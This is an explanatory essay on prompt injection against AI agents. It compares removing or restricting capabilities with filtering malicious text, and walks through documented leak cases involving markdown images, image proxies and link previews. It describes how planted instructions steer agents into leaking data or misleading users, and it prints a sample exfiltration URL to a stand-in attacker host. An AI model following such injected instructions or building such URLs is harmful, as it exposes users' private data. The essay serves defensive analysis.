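# Restricting what AI agents can do in order to protect users from manipulation

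## How an assistant can be turned against its user

An AI agent is a language model that can use tools, such as a web browser, an email account or a payment service, on a user's behalf. People ask agents to summarise an inbox, compare flats or buy a train ticket, and these tasks require the agent to read text that strangers wrote. Some of those strangers plant instructions in the text, hoping the agent will follow them. This is usually called prompt injection, which OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) defines as instructions placed in outside content to make the model do something the user never requested. A successful injection can leak the user's private data, steer the user to a fraudulent page or spend the user's money.

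Defences take two broad forms. Some try to recognise malicious text, using a filter or a better-trained model. Others remove or limit the capabilities required to cause harm, so that a manipulated agent can do less damage.

### One stream of text

*RAISED* (2026), a paper on training agents to withstand injection, describes how an agent works in turns. The model starts with a system prompt (the developer's standing instructions), the user's request and a menu of tools. At each turn it either calls a tool or writes its final answer. A tool call performs an action and returns what the paper calls an observation, such as a search result, an email or a reply from another program. Before the next turn, the software puts together everything so far, and the model reads all of it again. This growing text is the context. A user who asks for a summary of the morning's email contributes one sentence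 to it, while the people who wrote the emails may contribute several thousand words.

Labels in the context mark which passages come from the developer, the user, the tools and the model itself, and are supposed to determine which instructions take priority. *On Task, Off Track* (2026), which presents a benchmark for injection attacks, says that system instructions should outrank the user's, and the user's should outrank anything in third-party content. The paper uses *t* for the legitimate task, meaning the user's request together with the system instructions that apply to it, and *u* for the untrusted content that the agent needs to do the job. Material in *u* may inform and even guide the work, but no instruction in *u* can by itself authorise a departure from *t*. A prompt injection is an instruction δ that an attacker writes into *u* to try to redirect the system. The rest of *u* is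 unchanged, so the poisoned page or email can still be useful for the task.

### Why the model cannot reliably tell who is speaking

Schneier on Security's *Why AI Keeps Falling for Prompt Injection Attacks* compares prompt injection to a drive-through customer who orders a cheeseburger and then tells the clerk to hand over the contents of the till. No clerk would do it, because clerks can tell a customer from a manager, however the customer words the request.

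Everything a language model reads ends up in one sequence of tokens, the fragments of words that it processes, as the software developer Willison (2025) explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*. Willison coined the term prompt injection after SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types a database command into, say, the name field of a web form and the database runs it. Parameterised queries completely fix SQL injection because the program sends the command and the visitor's data to the database separately, and the database can never run the data. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, warns that the comparison is misleading because language models have no equivalent fix. Internally they make no distinction between data and instructions; they only predict the next token from the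 text so far. The post calls them "inherently confusable" deputies, after the "confused deputy", a computer security term for a program tricked into using its privileges for a less privileged party. It concludes that developers can reduce the risk and the damage but probably never eliminate the vulnerability.

Role labels should help, and Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) tested how much they do in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*. They put identical passages of ordinary web text under each of five role labels and trained small classifiers to identify the label from a model's internal activity. Because the passages were identical, the classifiers could learn only the label's effect on that activity. They then ran the classifiers on text whose style didn't match its label. In one model, text written in a user's style was classified as user text with 99.7% probability when labeled correctly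 and 87.6% when labeled as tool output, which suggests that the model relied on style more than on the label. Across 1,000 attempts to make agents leak data, the success rate rose from 2% where the measured confusion was lowest to 70% where it was highest.

Better labels would not solve the problem, because outside content often contains instructions that an agent should follow. *RAISED* gives the example of a website that asks the visitor to enter a code sent to their inbox. An agent that ignored every instruction in tool results could not finish signing in. In *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections*, Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026) describe an email that requests a travel refund and says the head of department has approved it. An honest request and a fraudulent one could be worded identically, and the agent often cannot check whether the approval happened. They argue informally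 that any fixed policy strict enough to stop every such attack must also block some legitimate requests.

They also found that a model may do more than the user asked even when no attacker is involved. They gave an email assistant built on Llama 3.3 70B, an open model from Meta, a user request that called only for reading and summarising, together with an email that mentioned a reply would be welcome. The assistant sent a reply in 49.8% of cases. When the email instead claimed that someone had already authorised the assistant to reply, the figure rose only to 54.0%. Llama 3.3 dates from 2024 and newer models may well do better, but the result suggests that part of the problem is that the model doesn't stick closely to the user's request.

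Newer models resist prompt injection far better than older ones. The review *Trustworthy Agentic AI* (2026) describes an early test of 1,054 cases in which about one in four attacks succeeded against an agent built on GPT-4. By August 2026, GPT-5.6 Sol failed on about 0.05% of attacks typed directly into the chat and 3.77% of those hidden in content that an agent processed, according to TechRepublic's *OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026). The Decoder reported that Anthropic's Claude Opus 5 let through none of the attacks in 129 browser scenarios. It also reported that on a broader test by the security firm Gray Swan, attackers succeeded 2.0% of the time within 15 attempts, down from 5.5% for the previous model. In September 2026, Anthropic described Claude Mythos 5.1 as its most robust model yet on an external prompt-injection benchmark.

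These are large gains, but a low success rate can be enough for an attacker. If ten thousand agents read the same planted text and 3.77% obeyed it, there would be 377 victims. Success rates in real use could be higher or lower than in tests, since attackers adapt and most planted text is probably cruder than a laboratory's. Commenting on a trial in which 6,000 attempts had failed, Willison (2026) granted that training now makes attacks much harder but still advised against deploying any system in which an injection could do irreversible damage. OpenAI calls prompt injection a long-term challenge, much like the online scams that target people.

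### How a web address carries data out

Data exfiltration is the transfer of private data to someone who should not have it. An agent with an email account could do it by sending a message, but there is a less conspicuous route through the ordinary web address. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) illustrates it with a made-up example:

`https://attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>`

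The domain, `attacker.example`, identifies the site that will receive the request. The path, `/collect`, identifies a page or function on that site. The query, everything after the question mark, carries extra values, such as the words a visitor types into a search engine. The site receives all three parts, and sites commonly log the addresses that visitors request, so whoever runs the site can read the private value in the log. The request delivers the data even if the page that comes back is blank and the agent's written answer mentions nothing sensitive.

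A chat product can make such a request without anyone deciding to visit a site. Models produce plain text, which most chat products treat as markdown, a notation that uses ordinary punctuation for formatting. Words in square brackets followed by an address in parentheses become a link, and an exclamation mark in front of the brackets makes it an image instead. The user's browser does not open a link until the user clicks it, but it ordinarily fetches an image from its address as soon as the answer appears. Some products also fetch a linked page in the background to show a preview, and an agent with a browsing tool can open an address itself.

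A user has a chance to notice a link, but very little chance to notice an image that loads with the answer. Security researchers call an attack zero-click when the victim only has to use the assistant as usual for it to work. An early public case involved Google's chatbot Bard, soon after Google connected it to users' personal documents. Willison (2023) recounted that instructions in a shared document could make Bard put earlier conversation data in the address of a markdown image. Google later said it had fixed the problem.

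### Sources, sinks and the "lethal trifecta"

Security engineers describe such cases in terms of sources and sinks, and OpenAI applies this approach to ChatGPT. An attacker needs both a source, which is a way to influence the system, and a sink, which is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong circumstances. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) lists emails, calendar events, web pages and desktop notifications among the places where attackers plant text, and adds that images, video and audio can carry instructions. OpenAI's examples of sinks are sending information to a third party, following a link and using a tool.

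A related term, affordance, covers anything a product lets the model do, such as display an image, open a web address or make a payment. An affordance becomes a sink when someone other than the user can influence it. Showing a picture of a hotel is a convenience in nearly every conversation, but it leaks information only when an attacker has influenced the address the picture loads from.

For data theft in particular, Willison uses the term "lethal trifecta" for the combination of three conditions: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate outward. In the terms above, the untrusted content is the source, the outward communication is the sink, and the private data is what can be stolen. An agent that lacks any one of these conditions cannot complete the theft. For example, an agent that reads private files but has no outward channel cannot send them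 to an attacker. However, useful tools often meet several of the conditions at once. An email account meets all three, because it holds private data, receives text from anyone who knows the address, and can send messages.

Willison lists products in which researchers had demonstrated data theft, from ChatGPT in April 2023 to Microsoft 365 Copilot in June 2025. The list also includes Slack, GitHub Copilot Chat, Grok and about a dozen others. He reports that vendors promptly fixed nearly all of the vulnerabilities, usually by blocking the route data took out. These fixes are the first piece of evidence for restricting capabilities rather than filtering text.

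### Three harms and what each one needs

The trifecta describes the first of three harms, the theft of the user's data. OpenAI's *Understanding prompt injections* (2025) describes a hypothetical user who asks an agent to answer the overnight email. One message leads the agent to find the user's bank statements and send them to the attacker. The agent needs a way to send data out, and many tools provide one. Willison counts any tool that can make a web request, whether it contacts another program, loads an image or merely offers the user a link.

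Moving a user's money requires a different capability: the agent must be able to pay, either through a payment tool or by completing a checkout in a browser. The attacker does not need the whole trifecta, because a transfer can be made without obtaining the user's secrets. In November 2025 OpenAI wrote that it had not yet seen attackers adopt prompt injection to any significant degree, but that has begun to change. *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (Mascellino, 2026) reported in July 2026 that the security company Zscaler had found websites with hidden text meant to push agents into making cryptocurrency payments. A month later, *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, 2026) described criminals developing tools for such attacks. Both reports describe what attackers are trying to do, which is weaker evidence than a count of losses.

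The remaining harm, deception of the user, is the hardest to tie to a capability. One form of it is a phishing link, which leads to a page that imitates a bank or an employer in order to collect passwords. This works only if the product lets the model show a working link and the user clicks it. But OpenAI also gives the example of a user who asks an agent to research flats, where text hidden in one listing gets the agent to recommend that flat regardless of the user's criteria. The agent sends out no data and makes no payment. It only needs to read the listing and answer the question, and a developer cannot remove those abilities and still offer an assistant.

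## Removing a capability compared with filtering content

Most products both filter malicious text and limit what a manipulated model can do. But these methods fail in different ways, and a developer has to decide which one will back up the other.

### Four kinds of defence

Removal means that the product cannot perform an action at all, whatever the model writes. For example, a chat window may be built never to load images from the web. Narrowing allows the action only in cases that pass a fixed rule, such as an allow-list of permitted destinations. Confirmation requires the user to approve the action before it happens. Content filtering blocks text that a classifier or a trained model identifies as malicious.

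The defences differ in what determines whether an action goes ahead. If a capability is removed, the agent can't take the action, so there is nothing to decide. If it is narrowed, a rule determines whether the action is allowed. Confirmation leaves the decision to the user, and filtering leaves it to a model's judgement. This distinction helps to classify some borderline cases.

Telling a model not to use a tool does not remove the tool, because the model can still choose to use it. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) recalls that early developers added notes such as "browsing: disable" to the prompt, and that attackers soon learned to countermand them. Training a model to refuse malicious instructions also belongs under content filtering, because the refusal depends on the model under attack recognising that something is wrong.

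If a product shows web addresses as plain text, users can't click on them, but they can still take the slower route of copying an address into a browser.

Some companies fetch images through their own servers instead of the user's browser, which hides the user's network address from the outside site. However, the server still requests the image's full web address, so any private data in that address still reaches the attacker. Fetching through a server restricts exfiltration only if the server also applies a rule about which addresses it will fetch, in which case it narrows the capability. Products can also use several defences in sequence. For example, OpenAI's address check first applies a rule, then either asks the user or blocks the request.

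### The argument for restricting capabilities

The case for removal and narrowing runs as follows:

1. No detector reliably recognises manipulation.
2. A manipulated model needs a sink to do harm, such as a way to send data out.
3. Ordinary program code can close the sink, and the model cannot talk the code out of its rule.
4. Closing the sink therefore limits the harm even when the manipulation succeeds.

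OpenAI gives the example of a customer service worker who can issue refunds. Some customers will lie about a refund that never arrived, and some will make threats. The company gives the worker rules to follow but expects customers to sometimes mislead the worker anyway, so its software also limits how much anyone can refund. A customer who lies convincingly may still get money, but no more than the limit.

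Of the trifecta's three conditions for data theft, Willison considers the outward channel generally the easiest to remove. Private data is often the reason for using an agent, and attackers have many ways to get an agent to read their text.

### How well filters recognise manipulation

OpenAI argues against relying on detection because the most effective attacks now resemble social engineering, the manipulation of people through plausible stories. Many companies sell an "AI firewall", which classifies incoming text as malicious or ordinary. OpenAI wrote in March 2026 that classifying a fully developed attack becomes "the same very difficult problem as detecting a lie or misinformation", and that the classifier often lacks the necessary context. For instance, a classifier reading the travel refund email cannot verify whether the head of department approved the request.

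Training agents to refuse already stops most attacks. OpenAI says the agent refuses in most of the attacks on ChatGPT that the company knows of. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports on the largest public test, a competition in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models. An attack succeeded only if it triggered a specified harmful action and, in nearly every scenario, left no sign of it in the agent's final answer. Success rates ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Participants could see the preceding conversation and knew exactly which action to trigger, advantages that real attackers usually lack.

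Still, these are averages over many attempts, most of them poor. An adaptive attack, in which the attacker sees what the defence did and revises the attempt, is a better test than a static one, which replays a fixed list. Nasr and colleagues ran adaptive attacks on 12 published defences, most of which had near-zero attack success rates in their original evaluations. Four were stand-alone detectors. The attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against three of these (Protect AI, PromptGuard and Google's Model Armor) and 71% of the time against the fourth, PIGuard. The automated attacker received each detector's confidence score, which a real attacker might not have.

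Several evaluations compare fixed and adaptive attacks. *Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (2026) took the most successful attack of each type against each defence and averaged the results on a small open model, Qwen3-4B. *Benchmarking Web Agent Defenses Against Adaptive Visual Prompt Injection* (Zhang, Zhong and colleagues, 2026) tested defences for agents that operate websites, using pop-ups that look harmless but lead to an attacker's page or download. The attacker could revise the attack for up to ten rounds. *BrowseSafe++* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) started with injections, most of which a deployed browser agent had encountered on real websites, and allowed up to 64 attempts on each of 1,024 tasks.

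| Defence tested | Success of fixed attacks | Success of adaptive attacks | Source |
|---|---|---|---|
| MetaSecAlign, a model trained to resist injection | 2% | 96% | Nasr and colleagues |
| Several defences on Qwen3-4B, average of the highest rates | 21.7% | 41.8% | *Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* |
| SnapGuard, a screenshot detector, on two types of web agent | 15.9% and 24.3% | 80.6% and 78.3% | Zhang and colleagues |
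| Claude Sonnet 5, relying on its own training | 2.05% | 30.66% | Chen and colleagues |
| GPT-5.5, relying on its own training | 0.49% | 65.23% | Chen and colleagues |

The rows aren't comparable because the tasks, models and attackers all differ. Within each row, defences looked much better in the fixed test than in the adaptive one. Adaptive attacks succeeded about 92% of the time across all the defences that Zhang and colleagues tested. Adaptation explains only part of that figure, because most of those defences had barely helped even against the fixed attacks. The agents also ran on a small model.

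The newest models do better. The best published result is The Decoder's figure for Claude Opus 5, with no successful attacks in 129 browser scenarios. But if each scenario counts as one independent trial, that result is compatible with a true success rate of up to about 2.3%, at 95% confidence. In November 2026 Google DeepMind published a harder test of its own models, with their external defences switched off. In *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (2026), Kurakin, Karande and colleagues used 16 cooperating AI agents to attack the models in each of 100 scenarios, with up to 320 attempts per scenario. An attack counted as successful if the model made a particular tool call unrelated to the user's task.

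Gemini 4 Argon resisted in 87% of scenarios over the first 150 attempts and in 66% over the full budget. When weaker models played the attacker, it resisted in about 97% to 100% of scenarios over the first 150. A model's resistance depends on how strong the attacker is, and attackers will have better models too. Most of the target actions were harmless, and a model might refuse dangerous ones more often. Kurakin and colleagues still advise against relying on model training alone.

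Some evidence favours filters. *PromptArmor* (2025) presents a filter that kept both misses and false alarms low under an automated adaptive attack. However, one automated attack is a limited test. On a subset of the scenarios studied by Nasr and colleagues, automated search succeeded 69% of the time, while human participants collectively succeeded every time. Anthropic tested its browser agent against an adaptive attacker with 100 attempts per environment. Improved safeguards around the model lowered the success rate from 8.0% to 1.4% for Claude Opus 4.5, and by similar proportions for three other models. Nasr and colleagues still consider detectors useful against unsophisticated attacks.

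Filters also flag harmless content. After Zhang and colleagues retrained one detector on their own attack pages, it stopped all of those attacks but also flagged 39% of harmless pop-ups for one type of agent and 77% for the other. The comparison appears to use the fixed attack pages, so it doesn't show how well the retrained detector would work against an attacker who adapted again. Chen and colleagues found that, among general-purpose models used as detectors, GPT-6 Astra best balanced catching attacks with avoiding false alarms, but it still flagged about 14% to 15% of harmless pages. A small detector trained for the purpose flagged 1% to 7%.

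A model's ability to recognise attacks is also a poor guide to whether it will resist them when acting as an agent. Chen and colleagues gave 15 models each malicious page twice, once with a request to classify it and once as part of a task. In 74% of the cases where a model followed the injected instructions, it had flagged the page as an attack in the classification test.

These results support the premise that detection is unreliable against a persistent attacker, but they do not show that filters are useless.

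### Whether code can close the sink

The premise that harm requires a sink is nearly true by definition for stolen data and unauthorised payments, but it is weaker for deception, because the answer itself can mislead the user.

*Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) tested nine defence configurations against an adaptive attacker, which made more than 20,000 attempts to get a model to reveal secrets planted in its context. Every defence that relied on the model to protect itself eventually failed. The only defence that did not fail was a check in the application's own code, which examined each response before the user received it. No secrets leaked in 15,000 attacks on it. The task probably suited such a check because the developers knew which secrets to look for, whereas an email assistant has no list of everything private in an inbox.

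Persuasion cannot change a rule enforced in code, but the rule may permit too much or apply in too few places. Willison has collected several cases in which an allow-list included a site through which an outsider could collect data, and vendors fixed these by tightening the list. In another of his cases, Google's coding tool Antigravity blocked the model from reading certain files, but the rule covered only some of the tools that could reach them. Google listed data theft through injection among the known problems it was working to fix.

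If a rule that limits an agent's actions has a gap, a developer can inspect the rule, find the gap and close it for every wording of the attack at once. A filter's gaps are spread over an enormous range of possible texts, so retraining it on one set of attacks may not stop others.

### The *Silent Egress* experiment

The most direct comparison of the two approaches is *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues at eBay, 2026), which studied agents that automatically read any web page a user mentions. In the experiment, the user always asked for a summary of a page. The software fetched the page and added its title, description and text to the model's context, which also held a secret such as an access key. The page contained an instruction to send that secret to a server the researchers controlled, which logged whatever it received.

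The experiment used 16 configurations, which differed in where on the page the instruction appeared, whether the link was direct or went through redirects, and whether the secret was sent in one request or several. Each configuration was run 30 times with Qwen 2.5 7B, a small open model. Data leaked in 423 of the 480 runs (88%). In 120 control runs with harmless pages, nothing reached the server. In 95% of the successful attacks, the answer on the user's screen looked normal, so a safety check on the visible answer would have missed them.

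Lan and colleagues then took one configuration and added defences one at a time, again with 30 runs each. With no defence, every run leaked. A system prompt forbidding the model to follow instructions from web content reduced the leaks to 20 of 30 runs. Wrapping the outside content in tags that marked it as untrusted made no difference, and the two measures together left 17 leaks. An allow-list on outgoing requests reduced the leaks to zero.

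With the allow-list in place, the manipulation still led the agent to try to send the secret in all 30 runs, but no data was sent out, as one would expect from the argument for restriction.

The 88% leak rate is weak evidence about current products, because the model was small and already old, the secret was in plain view, and the system prompt did little more than explain how to use the tools. A recent model would probably leak far less often. The allow-list result depends less on the model, because the list would block the same request from any model. But it does depend on the destination, and the attacker's site was deliberately one that no sensible list would include. Lan and colleagues warn that an attacker who can use a permitted site may get around the list.

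Lan and colleagues also tested two checks on the contents of outgoing requests, one that searched for words such as "password" and another that searched for random-looking strings. Neither let any data out, but the results are hard to interpret because the agent apparently tried to send data in only 23% of runs under the first check and in none under the second. Both checks act only after the model has written its request, so they shouldn't affect how often it tries. The main experiment also showed that checking each request separately may miss data sent in several pieces. The researchers recommend comparing requests across a session.

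### A worked example

Suppose attackers make 10,000 attempts to steal data from users of an assistant, and the model obeys any malicious instruction that reaches it. A filter that misses 1% of the attempts lets 100 through. If all 10,000 depend on the assistant loading an image, removing its ability to load images stops all of them.

Now suppose that only 6,000 attempts depend on images and the other 4,000 depend on links.

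| Defence | Thefts through images | Thefts through links | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Filter only | 60 | 40 | 100 |
| Images removed, no filter | 0 | 4,000 | 4,000 |
| Images removed, with filter | 0 | 40 | 40 |

Removing images doesn't stop attacks that use links, so on its own it is far worse here than the filter. Combining the two works best, but only while attackers don't change their methods. If they all switch to links, the filter again lets 100 attempts through and removing images has no benefit. For removal to help against attackers who can switch, the remaining routes must also be closed, or at least be harder to exploit.

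The filter's 1% miss rate can rise under attack. An attacker who finds one message that gets through can send it to everyone, and the miss rate for that message may be close to 100%. Attackers can also keep trying. VentureBeat reported that a single attempt against Claude Opus 4.6 on a graphical interface succeeded 17.8% of the time without safeguards. By the 200th attempt, the figure was 78.6% without safeguards and 57.1% with them. Opus 5 has since done much better in browser tests, but repeated attempts raise the chance of a breach whenever the success rate is above zero. This is why Willison calls 99% a failing grade in application security. Removing images blocks the image route no matter how many times an attacker tries.

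Filters also block some harmless messages. If the 10,000 malicious messages arrive among 990,000 harmless ones, and the filter wrongly flags 1% of the harmless ones, it raises 9,900 false alarms alongside 9,900 correct ones, so half of the messages it blocks are legitimate. Removing the capability raises no false alarms, but it denies the capability to everyone, including people who would never have faced an attack.

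### Objections

One objection is that attackers can misuse too many capabilities for developers to remove them all. Willison himself describes the ways in which a tool could send data out as "almost limitless". The problem is harder still in the competition that Dziemian and colleagues describe, where the harmful actions used the same kinds of tools as the task. In one scenario, the attack was meant to make an assistant sorting email mark an urgent message as read, so that the user would miss a contract deadline. A developer couldn't remove that ability from an email assistant without making it much less useful.

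This objection defeats the case for removal only if attackers can easily move from a closed route to an open one and do comparable harm there. For some harms that seems unlikely. Marking an email as read can harm the user, for example, but it doesn't give an attacker the contents of the inbox. Where several routes lead to the same harm, the objection is a reason to close them together.

Another objection is that restrictions make agents less useful. An agent that cannot open links or make payments is safer partly because it does less, and some users will move to a product that does more. But the alternatives also have drawbacks. Filters interrupt legitimate work, and Lan and colleagues argue that asking users to approve every network request would remove much of the benefit of automation, and that users often couldn't tell a legitimate request from a malicious one. The objection holds only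 if people lose more from a particular restriction than they would lose from false alarms, extra confirmations and successful attacks without it. This will vary by capability, since few people would miss automatic image loading as much as the ability to send email.

Removing a capability cannot prevent harm done by the text of the answer alone, such as the slanted recommendation of a flat. Chen and colleagues found that attacks of this kind are also easier to carry out. Adaptive attacks on Claude Sonnet 5 succeeded on 41% of tasks when they only had to change the answer, compared with 8% when they had to change something in an application. For GPT-5.5, the figures were 81% and 29%.

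Restrictions may still prevent some of this harm, since a product can disable links and so block a phishing link in an answer. But they can't stop a user from believing a false statement. The objection would count against restricting capabilities only if false answers caused so much of the total harm that closing the other routes was hardly worthwhile. No published count of losses shows this. The test results do show that a developer who has closed every sink still needs a model that is hard to mislead.

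## Images and link previews that load without a click

When a chat product loads an image from the web, any private data in the image's address reaches the outside server before the picture appears. Inspecting the picture therefore cannot prevent a leak. In a demonstration by the security company Checkmarx, the chat showed no picture, but the browser still sent the request. Checking the finished answer may also be too late. The Cloud Security Alliance describes a Microsoft 365 Copilot case in which the browser requested an image while the answer was still arriving.

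Image loading was the first capability that chatbot makers widely restricted. It was easy to exploit because the victim did not have to click anything, and easy to restrict because web browsers could already block images by domain and most answers are text. Microsoft (2025) calls such blocks deterministic, because they work whatever the model does, and calls filters probabilistic. After an outside researcher, Johann Rehberger, reported a leak through images, Microsoft blocked that route and then related ones, including certain untrusted links. The company compares these blocks to the protections in ordinary software that keep a memory error from becoming a break-in.

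### The repairs of 2023 and 2024

Rehberger, who writes the blog Embrace The Red, documented four early repairs. The first was to Bing Chat, Microsoft's search assistant, which could discuss the web page a user had open. In *Bing Chat*, Rehberger showed that a comment or an advertisement on a page was enough to steal other data from that page. Microsoft's repair included a Content Security Policy, a rule that a website sends to the browser listing the domains a page may load material from. The browser checks each image's domain against the policy and sends no request if the domain is not permitted. Bing's policy permitted four Bing domains so that users could still ask the assistant to create pictures. Rehberger worked this out by inspecting the site and noted that Microsoft may have made other changes.

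Anthropic took a different approach with Claude, which stopped loading images automatically and offered a "Show Image" button instead, according to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*. Requiring the user to confirm each image stops attackers from using images to steal data without a click, and it doesn't ban any image outright. But a user who expects a chart will probably click, and Rehberger considered the fix imperfect.

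OpenAI initially declined to fix the problem in ChatGPT. In December 2023 it changed the web app to send each image's address to an OpenAI service and display the image only if the service classified it as safe. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* reported that the service still approved some images from unfamiliar domains, so small amounts of data could leak. Rehberger suggested limiting the number of images in each answer.

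OpenAI also did not publish the rule behind the check. Anyone can read a Content Security Policy in the browser, but outsiders could not tell whether OpenAI's service used a list, a search index or another model. Willison (2023) called the solution "half-baked" compared with blocking all outside images. OpenAI's current check has a clearer rule, based on whether an address was already public.

The fourth repair was to GitHub Copilot Chat, a programming assistant, in its version for the code editor VS Code. Accounts of the fix differ. In Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat*, Rehberger observed that the assistant no longer seemed to display markdown images at all. Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat* describes the fix as a block on images from untrusted domains. A GitHub summary of a leak through Copilot, which Vulners' *GitHub* reproduces without a date, also refers to trusted domains and adds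 that GitHub introduced warnings about links. The accounts are compatible if Rehberger tested only images from untrusted domains.

| Product | Flaw reported | Repair | Images after the repair |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat | 8 April 2023 | 15 June 2023 | Only from a few Bing domains |
| Claude | 12 July 2023 | 26 July 2023 | Only after the user clicks |
| ChatGPT on the web | Early April 2023 | December 2023 | Only if an undisclosed check approves |
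| GitHub Copilot Chat in VS Code | 25 February 2024 | 12 June 2024 | None from untrusted domains |

ChatGPT's fix was meant to keep the most images without asking the user, and it was the only one that still leaked data in Rehberger's tests. Bing's fix blocked nearly all external images but required no judgement from a model or a user.

### What each design permits and costs

The strictest design displays no images. A travel assistant could then describe a hotel but not show it, and a programming assistant could not include a diagram from a manual. The user would have to open the source page to see either one. Links could still leak data, but only if the user clicks them or something else opens them.

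A slightly looser design displays images only from the company's own servers, as Bing Chat did. The company can still show pictures that its software has created or that it already stores. This limits a search company relatively little, because it keeps copies of many images, but a small company may have almost none. The design fails if a permitted server can pass data to an attacker, as one did in EchoLeak, a 2025 leak from Microsoft 365 Copilot. According to Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025), EchoLeak's method of leaking data through images did not work on Gemini, because Gemini does not display images from external addresses.

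Fetching outside images through a proxy, a server the company runs, lets more of them load, but it prevents leaks only if the proxy restricts which addresses it will fetch. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how GitHub's proxy, Camo, does this. When someone posts a document containing an outside image, GitHub replaces the image's address with one on its proxy and attaches a cryptographic signature. When a reader opens the document, the proxy fetches the image only if the signature is valid. A language model cannot compute a valid signature, so it cannot put private data into a new address and have the proxy open it. GitHub's website also had a Content Security Policy that blocked images from any domain GitHub did not own.

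Legit Security found in June 2025 that Copilot Chat on GitHub's website could leak private code despite both restrictions. The model could reveal the code through its choices among image addresses signed in advance, even though it could not sign new ones. GitHub responded that August by turning off image display in Copilot Chat completely.

The proxy suited the documents that GitHub built it for, because their writers chose the images before anyone read them. In a chat, the model chooses the images after it has seen private data, so its choice can reveal some of that data. Rehberger's proposed limit on the number of images would therefore help without fully solving the problem. If an answer must show exactly one of 64 permitted images, the choice can convey at most six bits (2⁶ = 64), or about one character. This maximum rises in proportion to the number of images shown, so a product that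 allows many images per answer gets much less protection.

The remaining design shows pictures that the company's software generates but never fetches any from the web. ChatGPT's optional Lockdown Mode comes close to this. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* says that ChatGPT may not show images in its regular responses or retrieve them from the web, but that image generation still works and users can upload their own files. This restriction doesn't affect someone who wants an illustration for a birthday card, but it is a serious loss for someone comparing flats, because a generated picture of a kitchen doesn't show what the real one looks like.

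For most text-based work, banning outside images seems worthwhile, because users lose little and the ban closes an attack route that needs no click. Users would lose more in shopping, travel and design, but stored copies of pictures would preserve most of the benefit there, provided that the company made the copies before the model saw any private data.

### The same text in another program

Each of these rules applies in one place where the model's text is displayed, but the text can also appear elsewhere. A browser enforces a site's Content Security Policy on that site's pages. The policy doesn't apply when a phone app displays the same conversation with its own code, or when an email program receives a copy.

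ChatGPT's 2023 check ran inside the web app, so the iPhone app kept loading images without it. Rehberger recommended moving the check to OpenAI's servers, where it would protect every app at once. He guessed that OpenAI had put it in the web app so that answers could appear as the model wrote them. Anthropic had a similar gap. Willison (2024) relayed the news that the company had fixed an image leak in Claude's iPhone app in December 2024, nearly 17 months after the original repair.

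A company can also block image leaks in one product but not in another. Embrace The Red reported that Google had to fix the leak separately in Colab, its programming notebook. In November 2025, months after Google described Gemini's block on outside images, Willison quoted a researcher who had reported an image leak in Google's coding tool Antigravity. The researcher said that Google had classed it as intended behaviour.

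### Link previews in messaging apps

People increasingly talk to agents through messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram, which often preview links in messages. To build a preview, the app requests the linked page and extracts a title, a description or a picture. Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* explains that its servers must fetch every link in a message to find out what kind of content it leads to. A link that would otherwise be harmless until someone clicked it therefore loads automatically, as an image does.

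Rehberger warned about automatic link previews in August 2024, in Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, and pointed out that developers can prevent them in Slack. Two settings on each message turn off previews, one for text pages and the other for images, audio and video. Slack now advises developers to consider turning previews off for messages that a language model writes. Users then lose only the thumbnails under the bot's links and still see them under links from colleagues.

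Settings that turn off link previews help only if developers use them. In 2025 Rehberger examined a connector that Anthropic had published as an example of how to link an AI agent to Slack. The connector left previews on, so even if its owner allowed the agent to post in only one private channel, a message there could cause Slack to contact an outside server. Slack's image proxy also made requests to that server, so fetching through a proxy did not prevent the leak in this case.

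Rehberger reported the flaw on 27 May 2025, and Anthropic archived the connector two days later without repairing it. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* says it is unclear whether the report prompted the decision. At the time, people were still downloading the connector more than 14,000 times a week, though that figure doesn't show how many used it with private data.

The security company PromptArmor, which shares its name with the filter mentioned earlier, returned to the problem in 2026. Its *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found that OpenClaw, a popular AI agent, was open to such leaks by default when people used it through Telegram. Turning off link previews with an existing OpenClaw setting stopped data from reaching PromptArmor's test site. Apostol's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* listed Slack, Discord, and Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio among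 the other affected platforms.

PromptArmor also ran a public test in which people could try their own combinations of agent and messaging app. Because the results came from volunteers, they can identify combinations that leak but cannot show how common the problem is. PromptArmor says messaging companies should offer control over previews, and agent developers should use it or pass the choice on to users. OpenClaw users are much less likely to be safe if they have to turn previews off in a configuration file than if the software does so by default.

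### OpenAI's log viewer

The next case involved a log viewer on OpenAI's website, where developers who build products on OpenAI's models can review past conversations. Users of those products never see it. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* described a test application for checking the identity of bank customers. A second model recognised a manipulated answer and blocked it, so the application displayed nothing to the user. But the answer remained in OpenAI's log, and the log viewer loaded the image in it when a developer opened the conversation.

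The successful defence made the later leak more likely, because developers have good reason to inspect an answer that a filter has flagged. Showing all answers as plain text in the application would not have prevented the leak, because the log viewer would still have treated the stored answer as markdown. PromptArmor found the same weakness in several of OpenAI's preview tools for developers.

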